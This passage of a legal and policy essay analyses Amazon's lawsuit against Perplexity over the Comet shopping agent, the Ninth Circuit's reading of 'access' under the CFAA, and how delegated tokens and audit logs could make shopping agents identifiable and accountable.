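The AI startup Perplexity released a web browser called Comet in 2025. It runs on the user's computer, as Chrome does, and includes an optional agent called the Assistant. Judge Milan Smith's appeals court opinion in *Amazon.com Services, LLC v. Perplexity AI, Inc.* (2026) gives the fullest neutral account of how Comet works. When a user asks the Assistant to find something on Amazon, it takes screenshots of the browser window and sends them to Perplexity's servers, which send back instructions for navigating the site. If the user has logged in to Amazon, the Assistant works inside her account.

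Browsers normally identify themselves to websites with a short piece of text called a user-agent string. According to Amazon's complaint, as reported in PPC Land's *Amazon sues Perplexity over covert AI agent access to marketplace*, Comet sent the same string as Google Chrome, so the Assistant looked like a human customer using Chrome. A distinct string would have let Amazon recognise the Assistant and block it. The companies dispute whether Perplexity knowingly changed the string after Amazon initially blocked the agent.

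Before Perplexity released Comet, Amazon told Perplexity's chief executive that the company's AI products could not use Amazon's store, and it repeated this afterwards. On 31 October 2025, *Demand to Cease and Desist* (Kaba, 2025), a letter from Amazon's lawyer, demanded that Perplexity stop using Comet's agents to "covertly intrude" into Amazon's websites. Four days later, Amazon sued under the Computer Fraud and Abuse Act (CFAA), the main US anti-hacking law, and a similar California statute. It argued that a trespass by "code rather than a lockpick" is still unlawful (Insurance Journal, 2025). Perplexity called the legal threats bullying.

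Both companies had commercial reasons for their positions. Perplexity said that Amazon wanted to suppress a competing product that undermined its advertising and upselling, and Amazon had launched its own shopping agents that year. But Amazon's stated demand seemed reasonable. In its complaint, quoted by the blog Educated Guesswork, Amazon says that agents entering customers' accounts must identify themselves so that it can check whether they put customers at risk.

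On 9 March 2026 Judge Maxine Chesney granted Amazon a preliminary injunction against Perplexity, which applies while the case is under way. She had called the decision a close call at a hearing, but her written order found strong evidence that Perplexity entered accounts "with the Amazon user's permission but without authorization by Amazon". She barred Perplexity from using agents on Amazon's systems and ordered it to destroy the Amazon data the agents had obtained (Jones Day, *Authorized by the User, Blocked by the Platform*, 2026). Perplexity appealed the next day, and stays kept the ban from ever taking effect (Sheridan, Brooks and colleagues, Ballard Spahr, 2026).

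### Who "accesses" a computer

To win under the part of the CFAA that Amazon relied on, a company must show that the defendant intentionally accessed a computer without authorization, or beyond what was authorized, and obtained information from it. The company must also have lost at least $5,000 within a year. Amazon counted the hours its staff had spent building tools to detect and block Comet toward this loss. The appeal depended on the meaning of "accessed".

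Perplexity's best argument was that none of its computers had connected to Amazon's, and the Supreme Court has read "access" as entering a computer system. The user's browser fetched each page from Amazon, and the Assistant then worked from the copy on her screen. Perplexity compared this to Apple's Safari browser filling in a customer's address and card details at checkout, which nobody would describe as Apple visiting Amazon. It also argued that any intention behind a purchase was the user's, because the software had none beyond her instructions.

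Amazon replied that Safari doesn't decide where to click. Perplexity's servers chose the Assistant's steps, and Perplexity itself had said that the agent "behaves like an efficient human shopper". Amazon also had a strong precedent from 2016, when the same appeals court held Power Ventures liable under the CFAA. Power Ventures, which ran a site that combined people's social networks, had kept sending messages through Facebook with its users' permission after Facebook ordered it to stop. Perplexity likewise had its users' consent and had ignored Amazon's refusal.

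According to a news report reposted on Stockopedia, Eric Tung, one of the three judges at the June hearing, tried out an analogy that favoured Amazon. He said the user might be "giving the key to Perplexity", which then lets itself in. He added that much of the case depended on finding the right analogy.

On 4 August 2026 the panel decided for Perplexity and cancelled the injunction. Its reasoning, as Judge Smith sets it out, goes like this:

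1. The CFAA applies to "whoever" accesses a computer, which means a person or an organisation. The Assistant is a tool, so it can't be the one who accesses Amazon.
2. That leaves the user and Perplexity. A company can be a "whoever", so the court had to ask whether Perplexity used the Assistant to enter Amazon's computers.
3. On the evidence so far, it did not. Receiving screenshots and sending instructions does not by itself amount to entering Amazon's servers. The user enters them, with the Assistant's help.
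4. If the statute is ambiguous, judges must read it narrowly. The CFAA is mainly a criminal law, and its words have the same meaning in civil suits as in prosecutions, so a wide reading here could turn ordinary customers into accomplices to a federal crime.

The court did not treat the 2016 Power Ventures decision as controlling because the judges in that case had assumed that the company accessed Facebook and considered only whether it had authorization. The legal commentator McCarthy (2026), in *Ninth Circuit Lifts Restrictions on Agentic AI Accessing Amazon*, had already called the March decision "a shockingly poor effort" to apply the CFAA to agents. The Electronic Frontier Foundation, a digital rights group, welcomed the result. It had argued that users, rather than Perplexity, operate Comet, and the court adopted its description of the tool.

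The fourth step seems the most persuasive. Congress wrote the CFAA to punish break-ins, and a customer who sends software into her own account is doing something very different. The third step is weaker because it depends heavily on where the browser runs. If Perplexity ran Comet in its own data centre and let customers direct it from their phones, a Perplexity computer would be connecting to Amazon's, and the court's reasoning would be much harder to apply, even though Doe would get the same purchase.

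### What the court did not decide

The August ruling concerns a preliminary injunction, so the judges asked only whether Amazon was likely to win on the evidence it had filed. They left open whether different facts might show that Perplexity controls the Assistant closely enough to have entered Amazon's servers itself. They also did not decide whether a customer's permission is enough to authorize access once Amazon has refused it. Judge Chesney had provisionally found in March that it is not, and the 2016 Power Ventures decision supports the same conclusion.

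The decision covers "access" under the CFAA and the California statute, on this record, and Judge Smith adds that it does not create "a new legal regime governing agentic AI". The panel expressly did not decide whether Perplexity could be liable in other ways for what the Assistant does, for example in a suit over harm it causes. So the phrase "the user accesses" does not mean that the user is liable when an agent makes a mistake. Amazon can still regulate access through its terms of service, according to a footnote.

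Amazon's evidence of danger was also weak. Its staff declared that the Assistant might not choose the best price or delivery method. Its security expert listed several risks, but only one involved a shopping site, which wasn't Amazon. Perplexity said that it had addressed the risks and that the expert couldn't fully reproduce them. Better evidence might have changed how the court weighed the harms, though not its reading of "access".

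Amazon asked the appeals court on 18 August to reconsider its ruling. MediaPost's *Amazon Presses Perplexity Shopping Agent Ban* (2026) quotes Amazon's complaint that the ruling "degraded website owners' ability to set the terms" on which agents may enter. MediaPost's *Appeals Court Again Rejects Amazon Bid To Block Perplexity* (2026) reported that the court refused on 10 September. The case continued in the lower court.

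### The block on Muse

Amazon then made two moves that *Amazon blocks Muse and takes Perplexity back to court* (Constantin, 2026) describes as relying on contract law instead of hacking law. On 20 September it began blocking Muse, a new assistant from Meta, after Meta had declined to remove Amazon from it. Customers who sent Muse to the store got a notice that an unauthorised agent "violates Amazon's Conditions of Use, to which our customers have agreed". The next day Amazon filed an amended complaint against Perplexity, which is the latest reported step in the case.

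Amazon's amended complaint accuses Perplexity of telling the appeals court something inconsistent with what its own servers did. Amazon has yet to prove this, but if it does, it may matter a good deal because the August decision relied on an account of what Perplexity's servers do and don't connect to.

Amazon says that Meta's Muse assistant doesn't identify itself while browsing and appears to capture and store customers' credentials. It also complains that agents bypass the personalised parts of its shopping pages. Bishop (2026), in *Amazon blocks Meta's Muse AI assistant in new standoff over agentic shopping*, describes the block as part of a wider fight over who controls the customer relationship when agents do the buying. A shop that can refuse agents can use that power to protect customers from a careless agent or to protect itself from a competitor, and outsiders will often find it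 hard to tell which it is doing.

Meta said at Muse's launch that the agent can use passwords and payment details from secure storage without seeing them. If it works as described, this is a broker like Deno's. It would not address Amazon's complaint about identity, because Amazon still receives a login by Doe when the broker fills in Doe's password.

### Why a developer might hide its agent

The August ruling weakens one legal reason for an agent to identify itself. Under the March injunction, a developer that ignored a shop's refusal risked being treated as a hacker. That risk is now much smaller for an agent that runs in the customer's own browser, at least in the western states the Ninth Circuit covers. Identifying itself can also get an agent blocked, and Amazon would have blocked Comet if Comet had announced itself.

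Delegation works only if the service supports tokens that identify the agent and the agent's developer wants the service to know about it. A signed token with an "act" claim is far better evidence of who is acting than a user-agent string, which any program can copy from Chrome. But nothing makes a developer request such a token, and an agent that has the user's password can log in as the user without disclosing that it is an agent. Developers also have no reason to identify their agents to a shop that would use the information only to refuse them.

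Contracts still give some reason to disclose, since Amazon's conditions require agents to identify themselves and the court left Amazon free to enforce its terms. Amazon's notice relies on its customers' agreement to those terms, so if the agent acts as Doe, Doe has broken them. Amazon presumably doesn't want to sue its own shoppers over a browser. It can close accounts or block sessions, but it first has to recognise an agent posing as a person, which NIST warns may not be possible.

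None of this means the court was wrong. The judges had to decide whether Congress meant to outlaw the conduct, while engineers who want agents to have identities are asking how to make agents accountable. A statute against computer break-ins is poorly suited to that purpose. If lawmakers want agents to identify themselves, they could require it directly and specify what a service may do with the information.

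### A mistaken purchase

Suppose Doe asks her agent to spend up to $150 on a replacement battery for her laptop. It orders a $129 battery that fits a different model. When the wrong battery arrives, she wants to know what happened.

If the agent used her login, her order history lists the battery as her own purchase. If the software keeps a history of the agent's actions, she may find the search and the wrong choice there. The shop's records contain only a normal login, a common browser and a valid card. When Doe writes to say that software made the mistake, the shop can't check, because a customer who had clicked on the wrong battery herself, or whose password had been stolen, could send the same letter.

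An auditor in this situation depends on records held by Doe or the agent's developer, and either may want to blame the other. The developer of an agent like Comet's receives screenshots of the session but may not keep them.

Now suppose the shop accepts delegated tokens and keeps the log fields that Microsoft recommends. Its record might look like this:

```
time             2026-12-05 14:02
on behalf of     doe
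agent            doe-shopping-agent
scope            buy one laptop battery, up to $150
action           order battery B7, $129
correlation ID   7f3a
```

Doe can see that the agent placed the order. She can withdraw its access without changing her password or logging out her phone. The shop can confirm that the order was within the agent's scope, so it did nothing wrong by accepting it. It can also search for other orders placed by the same agent software. If forty customers received batteries that didn't fit, the fault is probably in the agent or the shop's product page, and the shop can suspend that agent while its developer investigates.

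The correlation ID is most useful to the auditor. It is a label that the agent's software attaches to a task and that every later system copies into its own log. The auditor can follow 7f3a from the shop's record to the agent's tool call, and from there to Doe's request. This can help the auditor tell whether Doe typed the wrong model number, or typed the right one and the agent picked the first search result. The shop's record alone isn't enough, because the scope is only "one laptop battery". Microsoft warns that a log of only the model's replies is useless for this purpose, since it leaves out the tool calls and the permissions behind them.

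Even the full trail doesn't settle who pays for the battery. The shop may reasonably say that Doe authorised a purchase up to $150 and got one, while she may reply that she asked for a battery that fits and the developer sold her an agent that couldn't buy one. A court or a refund policy would have to decide between them. The trail narrows the argument to what each party did, which they might never establish under a shared login.

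It also has a drawback for Doe, because the shop learns that she uses an agent, and which one, and could use that information to refuse the agent or treat her differently. Someone who thinks of the agent as her tool may feel that this is none of the shop's business.

### What would settle it

A final judgment in Amazon's case could establish, on full evidence, how much control Perplexity's servers have over the Assistant and whether that control amounts to access. A ruling on contract might matter more, because it could show whether a shop can enforce its rules against an agent's developer or only against the customer. The August decision doesn't bind appeals courts in other parts of the US, which may read the CFAA differently.

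Court rulings will decide what developers may do, but people may keep sharing their logins with agents unless large services offer delegated access. Amazon's spokesperson compared shopping agents to food delivery apps, saying the apps should respect a restaurant's decision about whether to take part. The comparison assumes that shops can refuse agents, but a restaurant can refuse a delivery app more easily than a shop can spot an agent's disguised browser. TechSpot's *Amazon is blocking Meta's shopping AI agent* (2026) reports that Amazon also plans to block agents from Google and OpenAI, so general delegated access to its store doesn't seem close.

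A large shop could run a useful test by letting customers approve an agent in a few clicks, with a spending limit and a button to cancel, while still allowing shared logins. The shop could then measure how many purchases by known agents came through each route. If most customers chose the delegated route, developers would have little left to gain by disguising their agents as Chrome, but if most kept giving agents their passwords, shops would still have to guess which customers are people.
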